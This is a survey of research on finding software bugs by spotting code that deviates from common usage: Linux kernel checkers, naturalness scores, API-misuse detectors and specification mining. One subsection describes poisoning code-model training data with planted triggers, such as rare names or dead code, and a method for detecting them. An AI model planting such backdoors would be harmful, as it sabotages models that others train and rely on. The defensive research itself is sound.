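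One caller of `seg_alloc` correctly tested the pointer with `IS_ERR`. The checker detected only comparisons with null, so it reported that this caller had failed to test the pointer. The report puzzled the researchers because the checker would require a null comparison only if it had found one somewhere. They searched its log and found that another caller, `newseg`, compared the pointer with null.

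That comparison was the real bug, because when `seg_alloc` failed, its disguised error code wasn't null and `newseg` treated it as a valid pointer. The kernel then wrote user and group numbers to whatever memory was at that address. It also stored the invalid pointer in a table for later use, so the damage was likely to recur.

The caller that followed the kernel's usual convention was wrong, so counting how all kernel code tests pointers would have favoured it over the correct caller, which departed from the convention. The relevant evidence was the inconsistency between two callers of the same function, and someone had to read `seg_alloc` to see which was right.

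The researchers then wrote a checker for this convention. If any caller tested a function's result with `IS_ERR`, every other caller had to do the same. They found 78 such functions in Linux 2.4.1 and checked 295 places, finding five errors and six false alarms. In all five errors, programmers had used `IS_ERR` on a function that returned an ordinary null, which `IS_ERR` doesn't catch. Engler sent these cases to the kernel developers in *[CHECKER] 5 possible mis-uses of IS_ERR* (2001). He wrote that he might be "misunderstanding some subtle trick", but the developers fixed all five.

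### Copied errors and telling names

Programmers had copied the serial-port mistake into 20 places, the sound-card driver's missing unlock into five drivers, and one use of memory after its release into seven places.

Copying a mistake doesn't hide a contradiction, because each copy contradicts itself, but it can inflate the results. If the 102 use-then-check bugs include every copy of the serial-port mistake, about a fifth of them are the same error. Copying does more harm to a method that relies on counting. If a rule applies in 100 places, one exception gives a z score of 3, five give 1.7 and 20 give −3.3. A mistake pasted often enough can therefore fall so far down the list that nobody reads the warning.

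A common practice can also outlast the reason for it. In a commercial system, the researchers found four places that tested whether a function called `GetFrame` had failed, although it no longer could. An early version could fail, and programmers kept copying the old tests after the function changed.

Counting is more reliable when combined with what Engler and colleagues call *latent specifications*, features of code that programmers use to communicate their intent to one another. Names are the simplest kind. When the checker looked for functions that release memory, it considered only those whose names contained words such as "free" or "dealloc". When it looked for paired calls, it found about 130,000 different sequences in Linux and gave priority to names such as "acquire" and "release". The security checker's main source of false alarms was functions that accept pointers from both ordinary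 programs and the kernel. Programmers marked the difference with variables called `from_user` or `to_user`, which the checker used to ignore the safe cases.

Names can also mislead. In May 2001 Engler reported that a function called `sys_shmat` wrote directly to an address from a user's program, which he said "seems pretty bad". The kernel developer David Miller (2001) replied that the code was fine because every caller passed the address of a kernel variable. Engler answered that he had taken the prefix `sys_` to mean that all the pointers came from users.

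### Rules without templates

Templates limit a checker to the kinds of rule that someone has thought of. Li and Zhou's *PR-Miner* (2005) removed this limit with a technique that shops use to find products customers often buy together. The tool converts each function into a list of the functions it calls and the variables and data types it uses, then searches for combinations that occur in at least 15 functions.

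One such combination came from Linux code for storage devices. Of 29 functions that created a record for a device and registered it, 27 also scanned for attached disks. The rule that the scan should accompany the other two steps therefore had a *confidence* of 27/29, or 93%. The two functions without the scan contained errors, which Li and Zhou reported to the developers. A template for pairs of calls couldn't have expressed this three-part rule.

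PR-Miner took 42 seconds to extract 32,283 rules from about three million lines of Linux code. Only 14% of the rules had just two elements. Li and Zhou read the 60 highest-ranked warnings, leaving 1,387 unread, and found 16 bugs, a precision of 27%. Another 20 warnings pointed to functions that correctly left a step for their callers, and the remaining 24 were plain false alarms. In PostgreSQL, a database program, the top 60 warnings contained only six bugs. These figures are much worse than those from 2001, but the comparison isn't entirely fair, because Li and Zhou read a fixed number of warnings instead of stopping when false alarms became too common.

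One false alarm concerned the rule that functions that change two particular fields in a record of network data also release the record. Of 481 such functions, 480 followed the rule. The exception, `skb_clone`, copies the record for its caller, which has to release the copy later. This exception was deliberate, even though the rule had a confidence of 99.8% and the 2001 formula would have given it a z score of about 7.2.

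Li and Zhou also recognised that copied errors could make a real rule look weaker. They suggested identifying pasted code first and counting each group of copies once.

### Combining the evidence

Counting needs many examples, which most functions don't supply. In *From Uncertainty to Belief*, Kremenek, Twohey, Engler and colleagues (2006) tried to identify which functions give their caller a resource that it must later release, and which functions take over the job of releasing it. In the five projects they studied, slightly more than half of the functions had at most two calls that the checker could use.

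A simple example has three lines of code that open a file with `fopen`, read from it with `fread` and close it with `fclose`. Each function either has the relevant role or doesn't, so there are eight combinations. Each combination gets a score from each piece of evidence, and the combination whose scores have the highest product fits best. A *factor graph* is a diagram that shows which pieces of evidence bear on which functions.

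Suppose that `fopen` supplies a resource, `fread` only uses it and `fclose` releases it. The three lines are then correct, which scores 0.9 because the researchers assume that about nine places in ten are free of errors. They give 0.8 to a function that supplies a resource, 0.7 to one that doesn't release it and 0.3 to one that does. The product is 0.9 × 0.8 × 0.7 × 0.3, or about 0.151. Dividing by the total for all eight combinations gives a probability of 48%. The next best explanation, that none of the functions has a special role, also makes the code correct and gets 28%.

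Three lines can't settle the matter, but other code can help. If another fragment opens a file with `fdopen` and closes it with `fclose`, evidence about `fopen` also bears on `fdopen`, because both depend on what `fclose` does. This method represents Dennett's assumption of good design as a number, which other evidence can outweigh.

Kremenek and colleagues tested the method on 100 to 200 randomly chosen functions from each project, which they classified by hand. The method was right about 80–90% of the time in four of the projects. It did worse on Linux, where identifying 70% of the functions that supply a resource meant also mislabelling 30% of those that don't. Because the functions were chosen at random, these figures are more representative than results from the top of a ranked list. However, they measure how well the method identifies what functions do, and the researchers didn't systematically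 count the bugs it found.

For the kernel of Apple's Mac OS X, using a list of ten telling strings in function names, such as "alloc", raised accuracy from 81.2% to 89.1%. Adding 100 functions that a person had already classified raised it only to 90.1%. Using names without evidence of how programs used the functions was much less accurate. In SDL, a library for games, the full method found more than 40 functions missing from the list used by Coverity Prevent, a commercial tool that grew out of the Stanford group's work.

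Kremenek and colleagues' method also estimated the probability that a function didn't fit the rule at all. In Linux, this was 0.99 for the function that tests for disguised error codes, the convention that had caused the trouble with `seg_alloc`. After a failure there is no resource to release, so hundreds of correct pieces of code had looked like errors. The researchers recognised the convention and changed the checker to allow for it.

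## Corpus studies of how predictable buggy code is

Checkers like those of Engler or of Li and Zhou compare code with particular rules, but much of a program falls under none of them. A language model estimates how likely each piece of a text is, given the pieces around it, so it can score every line of a program by how unusual it is compared with common practice. If mistakes tend to look unusual, a programmer could find bugs by reading the most unusual lines first.

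### How a model scores a line

Language models divide code into *tokens*, which are the names, numbers and symbols in each line. The model gives each token a probability, and the token's surprise, in bits, is −log₂ of that probability. A token with a probability of one half has a surprise of 1 bit, and each further halving adds another bit. *Cross-entropy* is the average surprise over the N tokens of a line:

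H = −(1/N) × [log₂ P(t₁) + log₂ P(t₂) + … + log₂ P(t_N)]

Each P is the probability of a token given the tokens before it. Suppose a model gives the tokens of the line `return count - 7` these invented probabilities:

| Token | Probability | Surprise in bits |
|---|---|---|
| `return` | 0.5 | 1 |
| `count` | 0.25 | 2 |
| `-` | 0.125 | 3 |
| `7` | 0.01 | 6.6 |

The surprises add up to 12.6 bits, so the cross-entropy is about 3.2 bits per token. More than half of the total comes from the 7. If the line ended in 1 instead, and the model gave the 1 a probability of 0.5, the cross-entropy would be 1.75 bits per token. The score can't show whether the 7 is a mistake, because the programmer may have wanted to count back a week.

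*Naturalness* is how predictable code is to a model trained on other code, so high cross-entropy means low naturalness. The simplest such model is the *n-gram model*, which predicts each token using only the n − 1 tokens before it, by counting what followed them in its training data. If `count -` occurs 400 times in that data and `7` follows it four times, the model gives `7` a probability of 0.01.

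Programmers also have local habits, which a count over a large collection misses. Ray, Hellendoorn and colleagues (2016), in *On the "Naturalness" of Buggy Code*, therefore used an n-gram model with a *cache*, a second set of counts taken from the file under examination. They give the formula in their 2015 preprint of the same title:

P = γ/(γ + c) × P_global + c/(γ + c) × P_local

Here c is the number of times the preceding tokens have occurred in the cache, and γ (gamma) sets how quickly the local counts take over. If γ is 1 and `count -` has occurred three times in the file, each time followed by 7, the probability of the 7 rises from 0.01 to about 0.75, and its surprise falls from 6.6 bits to 0.4. The cache makes the programmer's own habits part of the norm, so a mistake repeated throughout a file also looks natural.

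The idea that code is natural in this sense comes from Hindle, Barr and colleagues (2012). Their paper, *On the Naturalness of Software*, found that n-gram models predict code better than they predict English. Some of that predictability comes from the language's syntax, which requires brackets and semicolons in certain places, and has little to do with what programmers choose. Pârtachi and Sugiyama (2025), in *Bringing Structure to Naturalness*, cite a 2019 study by Rahman and colleagues, who removed such tokens and found code less predictable than earlier work had claimed.

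### Buggy lines in ten Java projects

Ray and colleagues tested whether less predictable code is more likely to be buggy. They identified bug fixes in ten open-source Java projects by searching commit messages for words such as "error", "bug" or "fix". They checked 300 commits by hand and found that this method had classified 96% of them correctly. They counted every line that a fix deleted or changed as buggy, and traced those lines back through earlier versions of the project.

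The published version covers 7,139 bug fixes, taken from the year in which each project had the most fixes. The preprint covers 8,296 from the projects' whole histories but leaves out changes that deleted more than 30 lines. To score a file, the researchers trained the model on all the other files in the same version of the project, so a line's score showed how unusual it was for that project.

Buggy lines had an average cross-entropy of 6.21 bits, compared with 5.34 for other lines. The table gives the differences for fixes of various sizes, using the middle of each range that Ray and colleagues report. Cohen's d is the difference divided by the typical spread of the scores. By convention, 0.2 is small, 0.5 medium and 0.8 large.

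| Size of fix | Share of bugs | Buggy minus other lines | Cohen's d | Buggy minus fixed lines | Cohen's d |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 line | 15% | 1.98 bits | 0.61 | 1.63 bits | 0.60 |
| Up to 7 lines | 44% | 1.16 bits | 0.36 | 1.01 bits | 0.34 |
| Up to 100 lines | 81% | 0.56 bits | 0.17 | 0.39 bits | 0.12 |
| Any size | 100% | 0.87 bits | 0.26 | 0.72 bits | 0.19 |

If the scores followed bell curves, a d of 0.26 would mean that a randomly chosen buggy line is more surprising than a randomly chosen other line about 57% of the time, compared with 50% by chance. For one-line fixes, the figure would be about 67%.

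Ray and colleagues suspect that the effect is weaker for large fixes because programmers often tidy up other code in the same change, so harmless lines are counted as buggy. That is plausible, but it doesn't explain why the effect grows again when the very largest fixes are included.

One example comes from Netty, a library for network programs. A programmer called `setSuccess` where the rest of the file used `trySuccess` in similar places. The wrong line scored 5.96 bits and the corrected one 1.34. Elsewhere in Netty, a programmer copied an error message about `maxChunkSize` and forgot to change the name to `maxHeaderSize`. The model had already seen the copied text, so the mistake scored only 2.70 bits, while the correct line, which was new, scored 8.45.

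Bugs that developers fixed within nine months were much more surprising than those that lasted longer (d ≥ 0.62). Fixing these short-lived bugs lowered the cross-entropy by about 2.7 bits, compared with only 0.09 to 0.18 bits for bugs that lasted between 9 and 24 months. Fixing still older bugs produced no consistent drop. Surprising mistakes may be easier to notice, or they may cause failures that users encounter sooner. Either way, a tool that flags surprising code will do best on bugs that developers would probably have found soon without it.

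### Reading the most surprising lines first

To test whether a difference in averages could help someone decide what to read, Ray and colleagues imagined a reviewer who reads lines from most to least suspicious and stops after 5% or 20% of the code. They plotted the share of bugs found against the share of lines read and scored each ordering by the area under this curve, which is larger when the reviewer reaches bugs early.

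When the reviewer read 20% of the lines, ordering them by raw cross-entropy did 42% better than a random order. At 5%, it clearly beat a random order in only three of the ten projects. The most surprising lines were often declarations, which introduce names new to the model. Loops are repetitive and score low, although they often contain bugs. The researchers therefore compared each line with others of the same grammatical type, and gave more weight to types that had often been buggy in the past. For fixes of up to seven lines, the adjusted order scored 93% better than a random one when the reviewer read 5% of the lines.

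That figure counts a bug as partly found, in proportion to how many of its lines the reviewer reads. When reading any one line counted as finding the whole bug, and fixes of all sizes were included, the adjusted order was no better than random at 5%, because large bugs cover so many lines that a random selection tends to include at least one of them.

The researchers also compared their adjusted order with two popular free tools, PMD and FindBugs, which look for known kinds of error. They used bugs reported after release in five of the projects. All three methods found about as many bugs for the same inspection effort. Ordering the tools' warnings by surprise within each priority level significantly improved their results.

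This comparison makes both methods look better than they would in everyday use. A tool got credit for any warning on a buggy line, even one about something else. The adjusted score reflected each project's record of past bugs as well as naturalness. Ray and colleagues acknowledge that the "reviewer" was a calculation and that no developers read the lines.

### Fixed lines that stay surprising

If unrelated changes had diluted the effect, removing them should strengthen it. *An Empirical Study on the Relationship between Defects and Source Code's Unnaturalness* (Jiang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) used several large collections of bugs whose collectors had already removed these changes. One such collection, *growingBugs*, has 1,911 bugs from Java projects. For each bug, it includes the buggy version, the fixed version, a patch containing only the changes that fix the bug, and at least one test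 that triggers it.

Buggy lines were often less natural than other lines, but the fixed lines were, on average, as unnatural as the buggy ones across the programming languages that Jiang and colleagues studied. They also used a program to insert small errors into working code, and these errors didn't significantly reduce the naturalness of the lines.

On average, correcting a mistake did not make its line more predictable, and inserting one did not make it less predictable. This suggests that mistakes are not what makes buggy lines surprising. The lines are probably surprising because of the task they perform. A programmer handling a rare piece of hardware, or an odd exception in a tax rule, writes code that few others have written, and so has few examples to copy and more ways to go wrong. The code is still unusual once it works. Jiang and colleagues conclude, more cautiously, that defects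 may not be the root cause of unnatural code.

The average change could also be zero because many fixes make code more predictable and many others make it less so. A fix can introduce a name that never appeared in that position in the model's training data, as the `maxHeaderSize` line did.

The disagreement with Ray and colleagues may also be smaller than it looks, because they too found little or no drop for bugs that had lasted more than nine months. If collections of carefully documented bugs contain fewer of the obvious bugs that developers fix quickly, the two studies partly cover different bugs. The one-line fixes are harder to reconcile with the later result, because they showed a drop of 1.6 bits even though they are unlikely to include unrelated changes.

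The one exception Jiang and colleagues found was bugs related to checks, such as a missing test of whether an operation succeeded. Fixing these did make the code significantly more natural. In an example from the older study, a programmer working on Lucene, a search library, created a directory without testing whether this had worked. The line scored 9.21 bits, and the corrected code, which follows the usual pattern of testing the result, scored 5.34. Unchecked failures were also the largest group of bugs that Engler and colleagues found by counting. Programmers check results in much the same way whatever their program is for, so a missing check is easier than most mistakes to distinguish from code that is unusual only because its task is.

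### Why a real correlation finds so few bugs

When Jiang and colleagues used naturalness alone to locate buggy lines, the precision was below 1%. Naturalness can still have a highly significant correlation with bugginess, because with enough lines a significance test will detect even a tiny difference in average naturalness between buggy lines and other lines. Precision depends on how much the two groups overlap and on how rare the buggy lines are.

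In *Exploring the Naturalness of Buggy Code with Recurrent Neural Networks*, Lanchantin and Gao (2018) trained a neural network that can use more of the preceding text than an n-gram model can, and tested it on Elasticsearch, one of Ray and colleagues' ten projects. Buggy lines were slightly less predictable, averaging 1.58 bits per character compared with 1.52 for other lines. The network separated the two groups slightly better than an n-gram model did. With 10,902 lines in each group, a difference of only 0.03 standard deviations would be statistically significant.

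The researchers tested equal numbers of buggy and sound lines, but in the code these came from, only 10,902 of 9,437,902 lines were buggy, or about one in 866. If surprise separates the two groups as well as it did in Ray and colleagues' full results, with a d of 0.26, and the scores are normally distributed, a tool that flags the most surprising 5% of the sound lines would also flag about 8.3% of the buggy ones. It would flag roughly 900 buggy lines and raise 471,000 false alarms, a precision of 0.2%.

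With the much larger d of 0.61 from the one-line fixes, the tool would catch 15% of the buggy lines, but its precision would still be under 0.4%. The likelihood ratio of a flag is about 1.7 in the first case and 3 in the second. It would have to be about 865 for a flagged line to have a 50% chance of being buggy.

Precision also depends on which lines count as buggy. Ray and colleagues counted every line that a fix changed, which made 2.2 million of 35.3 million lines buggy, or about 6%. At that rate, the same tool with a d of 0.26 would have a precision of about 10%. Excluding changes unrelated to the bug leaves fewer buggy lines to find, which lowers precision even if the model works just as well.

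### Later measures

*CodeBERT-nt* (2022), by Khanfir and colleagues, measures naturalness with CodeBERT, a neural network already trained on a large amount of code, instead of n-gram counts. The method hides tokens in a line, has the network guess them, and uses its lowest confidence in any hidden token as the line's naturalness score. Using the lowest value prevents averaging from hiding one very unlikely token, and because CodeBERT is already trained, the method doesn't need a new model for each project.

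All these methods score each line more or less in isolation, so they miss mistakes that come from combining ordinary lines in the wrong way. Yang, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Dependency-Aware Code Naturalness*, give an example in which each line is common, but together the lines can crash the program by using an object while it is still null. Their method traces which lines affect which others, groups up to three connected lines, and scores each group as a whole.

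They tested the idea on three collections of Java bugs by ranking the lines of each buggy file. The score compares each ranking with a perfect one, which scores 1, over the first fifth of the lines. Grouping connected lines raised the n-gram model's scores from 0.105–0.151 to 0.133–0.194 and CodeBERT's from 0.050–0.082 to 0.064–0.115.

By this score's definition, a random order should get about 0.1 when buggy lines are rare. The grouped n-gram model was therefore somewhat better than chance, while CodeBERT was worse than chance on two of the three collections, even with grouping. Yang and colleagues say they weren't trying to compete with the best bug finders.

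They also tried a larger model, CodeLlama, with 13 billion parameters. They tested it on well-written programs that they had made odd without changing what the programs did, for example by adding a loop that achieved nothing. Grouping lines helped CodeLlama too, but its scores changed by only 5% to 11% on average, compared with 20% to 41% for the small n-gram model. The two models' scales may not be directly comparable, but the result gives no reason to expect larger models to be more sensitive to odd code.

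Pârtachi and Sugiyama instead scored code by its *syntax tree*, a diagram of the code's grammatical structure. Ruby was slightly more predictable this way than with an n-gram model, at 8.5 bits against 9.0, but Java, JavaScript and Python were much less predictable. They then used what the Java model had learned to predict which changes to two Java projects would introduce bugs.

The predictions had an average precision of about 30% in both projects, with a recall of 22% in one and 42% in the other. These figures are far above 1%, but the task was easier because the method judged whole changes instead of single lines and learned from examples of changes that had introduced bugs. Pârtachi and Sugiyama still consider the precision too low for a tool that interrupts developers.

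In *What Makes Software Bugs Escape Testing?*, Cotroneo, De Rosa and colleagues (2026) tested whether naturalness can identify the most damaging bugs, those that testers miss and users run into. They compared about 7,100 such bugs with the same number that developers caught before release, in C, C++ and Java projects. Cross-entropy didn't significantly distinguish the two groups. Code age distinguished them much better, especially in C and C++, where the missed bugs were in considerably older functions. Cotroneo and colleagues suggest that old code depends on assumptions that built up over the years and that nobody wrote into the tests, and a model that measures how unusual tokens are has no access to those assumptions.

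Another study from 2026, *Model See, Model Do?*, gave code-writing language models pairs of buggy and fixed code. The models consistently assigned a higher probability to the least likely token in the fixed code than to the least likely token in the buggy code. When the models wrote the code themselves, they produced the buggy version much more often.

The two results can both be true. Suppose the versions differ in two tokens, which have probabilities of 0.6 and 0.2 in the buggy code and 0.3 and 0.3 in the fix. The buggy code contains the least likely of these tokens, but the model will write the buggy pair 12% of the time and the fixed pair only 9% of the time. Whether a model scores correct code higher therefore depends on how the score is calculated from the token probabilities. Comparing two versions also requires a fix, which a programmer looking for unknown bugs doesn't have.

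### Code that is surprising on purpose

People can also write surprising code deliberately. Some attackers plant code in the public collections that companies use to train code models, so that a model trained on it will misbehave when its input contains a certain trigger. The trigger may be a rare name or a few lines that can never run, such as code that prints "fail" if a random number is below zero.

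Sun, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *Show Me Your Code! Kill Code Poisoning*, detect such triggers with an n-gram model trained on a small amount of clean code. They delete tokens one at a time and look for those whose removal makes the code more natural across many samples. In 20 test scenarios, the method found all the planted samples and wrongly flagged 8.3% of the clean ones on average. Pooling the samples was essential, because removing a normal token from a single piece of code can also make the rest look more natural.

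The attackers meant every token they planted, so the planted code is a deliberate exception. Harmless deliberate code can score just as high. In the Facebook software that Ray and colleagues studied, a programmer added a correct line to start recording the program's activity, and it scored 9.89 bits because nothing like it had appeared in the project before. The wrong function call in Netty, a slip, scored only 5.96 bits.

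## Audits of false alarms in tools that learn from common usage

A line of code can look unnatural just because few programs do the same job. Comparing only code that uses the same software library can reduce this problem. A library is a collection of ready-made functions, and its *application programming interface* (API) is the part that other programs can call. Thousands of programs may call the same function, so a tool can learn how most of them use it and report any that use it differently.

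### How a detector learns a library's rules

An *API misuse* is code that uses a library in a way the library forbids. For example, Java programs often go through a collection with an iterator, an object that supplies the items one at a time. The function `next` supplies an item, and `hasNext` tests whether any are left. Calling `next` when none are left causes an error that can crash the program, so the programmer must first make sure an item remains.

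Most API-misuse detectors work much like PR-Miner. They record which functions each piece of code calls, and sometimes the order of the calls, then report code that contains most but not all of a frequent pattern. Jadet, for example, requires at least 20 examples of a pattern. It reports code that lacks one or two parts of the pattern if such code is at least ten times rarer than the pattern.

Another detector, DMMC, looks for a single missing call. It counts the places that call exactly the same functions on an object as the code under examination (E), and the places that call those functions and one more (A). It then calculates a strangeness score:

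strangeness = 1 − E / (E + A)

DMMC scores a possible missing call by the share of similar code that makes the call, and reports anything above 0.97. If 2 places make the same calls and 98 make those calls plus one more, the score is 0.98. Like the count of locks, the score measures how dominant the norm is and can't distinguish slips from deliberate exceptions.

### Seventeen misuses in 230 reports

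*A Systematic Evaluation of Static API-Misuse Detectors* (Amann, Nguyen and colleagues, 2017) surveyed 12 detectors. The detectors' developers had reported precision from about 5% to 90%, but they had used different projects and different definitions of a bug, and none had measured recall. The 90% figure came from a tool that looked only for faulty error handling.

Amann and colleagues ran four Java detectors on the same five open-source projects: the two that produced the most reports, the two that produced the fewest, and one chosen at random. Two researchers independently judged each detector's 20 highest-ranked reports on each project, or all of them if there were fewer than 20. They were lenient and accepted, for example, a report that a call to `hasNext` was missing even if it didn't mention that the program also has to act on the result.

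| Detector | Reports judged | Confirmed misuses | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tikanga | 44 | 5 | 11.4% |
| Jadet | 39 | 4 | 10.3% |
| DMMC | 81 | 8 | 9.9% |
| GrouMiner | 66 | 0 | 0% |
| Total | 230 | 17 | 7.4% |

The differences between the first three are too small to mean anything in samples of this size. Two of the researchers had helped to develop GrouMiner, so bias against it probably doesn't explain its 0%. As with Engler's ranked lists, these figures describe only the most promising reports, not all deviations.

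Only 14 of the 17 confirmed misuses were distinct, and all 14 were missing checks before a program took an item from a collection. Missing checks were also the bugs that stood out most clearly in Jiang and colleagues' study of naturalness. Judging a report took about five minutes, so each reviewer spent more than an hour for every confirmed misuse.

### Correct code that looked wrong

Amann and colleagues also identified the cause of each of the 213 false alarms. The largest group, 73 of them (34.3%), concerned code that was uncommon but correct. Many of these involved Java maps, which store key-value pairs, much as a dictionary pairs words with definitions. Most code that handles such a pair calls both `getKey` and `getValue`. Jadet and DMMC learned that the two calls belong together and reported code that made only one of them. Jadet also reported code that made them in an unusual order.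 But a program that needs only the keys has no reason to call `getValue`, and the library doesn't require it to. In 42 cases, the detectors reported a missing or reordered call of this kind.

The detectors were right that the two calls usually occur together, but they do so because most programmers happen to want both pieces of information. The pattern reflects a common purpose and doesn't show what someone with a different purpose should do.

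Another 41 false alarms (19.2%) flagged correct alternatives to the usual pattern. For example, instead of calling `hasNext`, a programmer can test whether the collection is empty before taking its first item, which is just as safe. These and the uncommon uses make up more than half of the false alarms, and in both groups the pattern was real but programmers didn't need to follow it.

The detectors analysed the code incorrectly in 51 cases (23.9%). Some missed a call because it was in another function, or did not detect that two names referred to the same object. Better engineering could prevent many of these errors, and they are not evidence against learning from common usage.

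Another 26 false alarms (12.2%) came from code that implements an interface for other code to use. One project combined two iterators into a new one, whose `next` function called `next` on one of the originals without always checking it first. This was safe because any code using the new iterator had to call the new iterator's `hasNext` beforehand. The comparison group was again the problem, because the detectors had compared code that implements an iterator with code that only uses one.

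In 14 cases (6.6%), a programmer kept two lists that always had the same length and checked only one of them. Amann and colleagues counted these reports as false alarms because the code worked, but they consider the practice dangerous, since a later change could make the lengths differ. The programmer might have welcomed a warning despite having made no mistake. The remaining eight false alarms had minor technical causes.

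### Fifty copies of the correct code

A tool with low precision might still be useful if it found most of the misuses. To measure recall, Amann and colleagues used MUBench, their collection of known misuses, most of which came from bug reports. In one experiment, they gave each detector a file containing a known misuse and 50 copies of the corrected code. They set the detectors to require 50 examples of a pattern, so the detectors could learn only from the copies. In a second experiment, the detectors had to learn from the projects themselves.

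| Detector | Recall with 50 correct copies (64 misuses) | Recall without them (53 misuses) |
|---|---|---|
| GrouMiner | 48.4% | 0% |
| Jadet | 23.4% | 5.7% |
| DMMC | 23.4% | 20.8% |
| Tikanga | 20.3% | 13.2% |

The second column makes the detectors look better than they were, because 14 of the 53 misuses were ones the detectors had found in the precision test. Of the other 39, DMMC found two and the other detectors found none. DMMC ranked those two 309th and 613th, so low that hardly anyone would have read them.

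Amann and colleagues conclude that the projects contained too few correct examples to learn from, and the drop in GrouMiner's recall supports this. But even with perfect examples, every detector missed more than half of the misuses. Their records of the code lacked some of the information they needed. For example, to decrypt a message, a program has to pass a particular value to the encryption library. None of the detectors recorded such values, so no number of examples would have helped them detect a wrong one.

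The experiment can't show whether more examples would reduce false alarms. The 50 copies provide no more evidence of correct usage than one example would, and they worked only because the researchers already knew that the code was correct. The researchers had in effect turned the usual pattern in the corpus into a specification, with no correct alternatives for the detectors to mistake for errors. The false alarms about `getKey` had a different cause. The detectors had seen enough examples to learn the pattern but drew the wrong conclusion from them.

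### A successor that made fewer kinds of mistake

*Investigating Next Steps in Static API-Misuse Detection* (Amann, Nguyen and colleagues, 2019) describes MUDetect, which the same researchers then built to remove these causes of error one at a time. It represents each piece of code as a graph of call order, data flow and which checks control which calls. It leaves "get" calls out of its patterns unless the code in the pattern uses their results. It also drops a report if the code fully matches another frequent pattern, and ignores most code in which a class uses its own functions.

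Amann and colleagues compared 34 ways of ranking the reports. The best one divided the number of times a pattern occurred by the number of times the same deviation occurred, and also accounted for how much of the pattern the code contained.

On ten projects, 32 of MUDetect's 146 highest-ranked reports were real misuses, a precision of 21.9%. The four older detectors had a precision between 2.6% and 8.8% on the same projects. MUDetect's recall was 20.9%, or 72.5% when the researchers supplied the correct code. The table compares its false alarms with those in the earlier audit.

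| Cause of false alarm | Four older detectors | MUDetect |
|---|---|---|
| Uncommon but correct | 73 (34.3%) | 84 (73.7%) |
| Errors of analysis | 51 (23.9%) | 18 (15.8%) |
| Correct alternatives | 41 (19.2%) | 0 |
| Partial uses inside a class | 26 (12.2%) | 1 (0.9%) |
| Objects that depend on each other | 14 (6.6%) | 5 (4.4%) |
| Other | 8 (3.8%) | 6 (5.3%) |
| Total | 213 | 114 |

The share of false alarms that were uncommon but correct uses more than doubled, mainly because MUDetect made fewer mistakes of other kinds. If 34 of every 100 false alarms are uncommon uses, and better engineering removes 54 of the other 66, those 34 make up 74% of the remainder. The reviewers also read a fixed number of reports, so when one false alarm dropped out of the top 20, another could take its place. But the number of false alarms from uncommon uses fell from 4.3 to 2.6 for each confirmed misuse.

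Part of the rise comes from how the researchers sorted the false alarms. *Root Causes of MD's False Positives and False Negatives*, which lists all of MUDetect's errors, includes five cases in which a programmer checked a collection's size instead of calling `hasNext`. The audit had counted such cases as correct alternatives, but this list classes them as uncommon uses because they were too rare for MUDetect to learn. Combining the two categories gives a smaller rise, from 54% to 74%.

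The same list shows how much a detector's results can depend on its threshold. In one project that handled PDF files, ten places read a number using `floatValue` and seven used `intValue`. Both are correct. MUDetect required ten examples of a pattern, so it learned only the use of `floatValue` and reported all seven uses of `intValue` as misuses. With three more uses of `intValue`, it would have learned that pattern too and raised none of these false alarms.

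### More alternatives and more examples

An older detector, Alattin, by Thummalapenta and Xie, was designed to learn rarer alternatives. It looks for a pattern that at least 40% of examples follow, then searches the remaining examples for patterns that at least 20% of those follow. Alattin accepts code that fits any of these patterns. According to Amann and colleagues, allowing for frequent alternatives raised its precision from 29.5% to 33.3%, and also allowing for rarer ones raised it to 37.8%. However, Alattin then missed 1.5% more misuses, because a mistake that enough programmers make looks like another correct alternative.

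Amann and colleagues tested the effect of more examples by letting MUDetect learn from other projects. For each API with a known misuse, they collected up to 20 examples from each of up to 50 projects. They counted how many projects contained a pattern instead of its total uses, so repetition within one project couldn't create a norm. Precision rose from 21.9% to 33.0% and recall from 20.9% to 42.2%.

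More examples clearly helped, although two in three reports were still wrong. The precision may be somewhat overstated, because the researchers supplied examples only for APIs with known misuses, which left fewer patterns that could cause false alarms. This version also missed 17 misuses that MUDetect had found by learning from the project alone. Ten of these involved functions that the project itself defined, perhaps because a project uses its own functions differently than outsiders do.

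The two versions of MUDetect found 27 misuses that nobody had reported before. The researchers sent fixes for 16 of them in eight batches, and developers had accepted three of the batches by publication. One of the accepted fixes stopped Google's Closure compiler from crashing on certain comments.

### Writing down the rules

*Specification mining* uses common behaviour to produce rules that people can read and other tools can check. Ammons, Bodík and Larus, in *Mining Specifications* (2002), recorded the function calls made by running programs and summarised the frequent sequences in a diagram, removing paths that programs rarely took. They relied on the observation that "common behavior is often correct behavior". *Topic 7*, a set of lecture slides on this kind of research, states the maxim without "often", as "common usage is correct usage".

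The researchers tested their miner on programs for X11, a system for displaying windows. When a user selects text to copy, the program has to claim ownership of the selection. According to a manual, it must also supply the time of the event that led to the claim, such as a mouse click. The researchers could therefore compare the mined rule with a written one.

The miner couldn't learn the rule from all the programs at once, because there were few programs and several broke the rule. So Ammons and colleagues started with one program and added the others one at a time, with an expert checking any that didn't fit the rule learned so far. Of the 15 programs they added, 11 didn't fit. Six of these were correct, but the draft rule was too narrow to include them. Three departed from the manual harmlessly, and two had bugs.

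The final rule closely matched the manual, but only because a person had chosen which programs the miner learned from. The three harmless programs deviated from the rule because they used the selection to exchange messages of their own, a purpose the manual didn't cover. Ammons and colleagues concluded that the manual needed clarifying.

### Giving good code more weight

Later miners produced far more false rules than real ones. Le Goues and Weimer, in *Specification Mining With Few False Positives* (2009), blame this on treating all code as equally good evidence. They compare mining to learning English grammar from school essays, where it makes sense to trust the students who are passing. Their miner looks for rules of the form "a must be followed by b". It takes into account whether programmers recently changed the code, whether they copied it from elsewhere and how readable it is. It also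 estimates how often the program would run the code, because testing is more likely to expose mistakes in code that runs often.

These measures can help because code that breaks a real rule contains an error, so it should tend to be worse than code that follows the rule. With a false rule, there is no reason to expect this difference. *Measuring Code Quality to Improve Specification Mining* (Le Goues and Weimer, 2012) gives an example from Ptolemy, a program for modelling designs, where code that gets permission to read some data must later give up that permission. Paths that followed this rule had an average predicted frequency of 39%, compared with 4% for paths that broke it. For a false rule about two other functions, the figures were 31% and 58%. Engler's z statistic had ranked the two rules close together.

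The 2009 study tested two versions of the new miner on more than 800,000 lines of Java and compared them with Engler and colleagues' method and an earlier miner by Weimer and Necula. One version balanced precision and recall, while the other, stricter version aimed only for precision.

| Miner | Real rules | False rules | Share of rules that were false |
|---|---|---|---|
| Engler and colleagues' method | 13 | 2,508 | 99% |
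| Weimer and Necula's miner | 68 | 567 | 89% |
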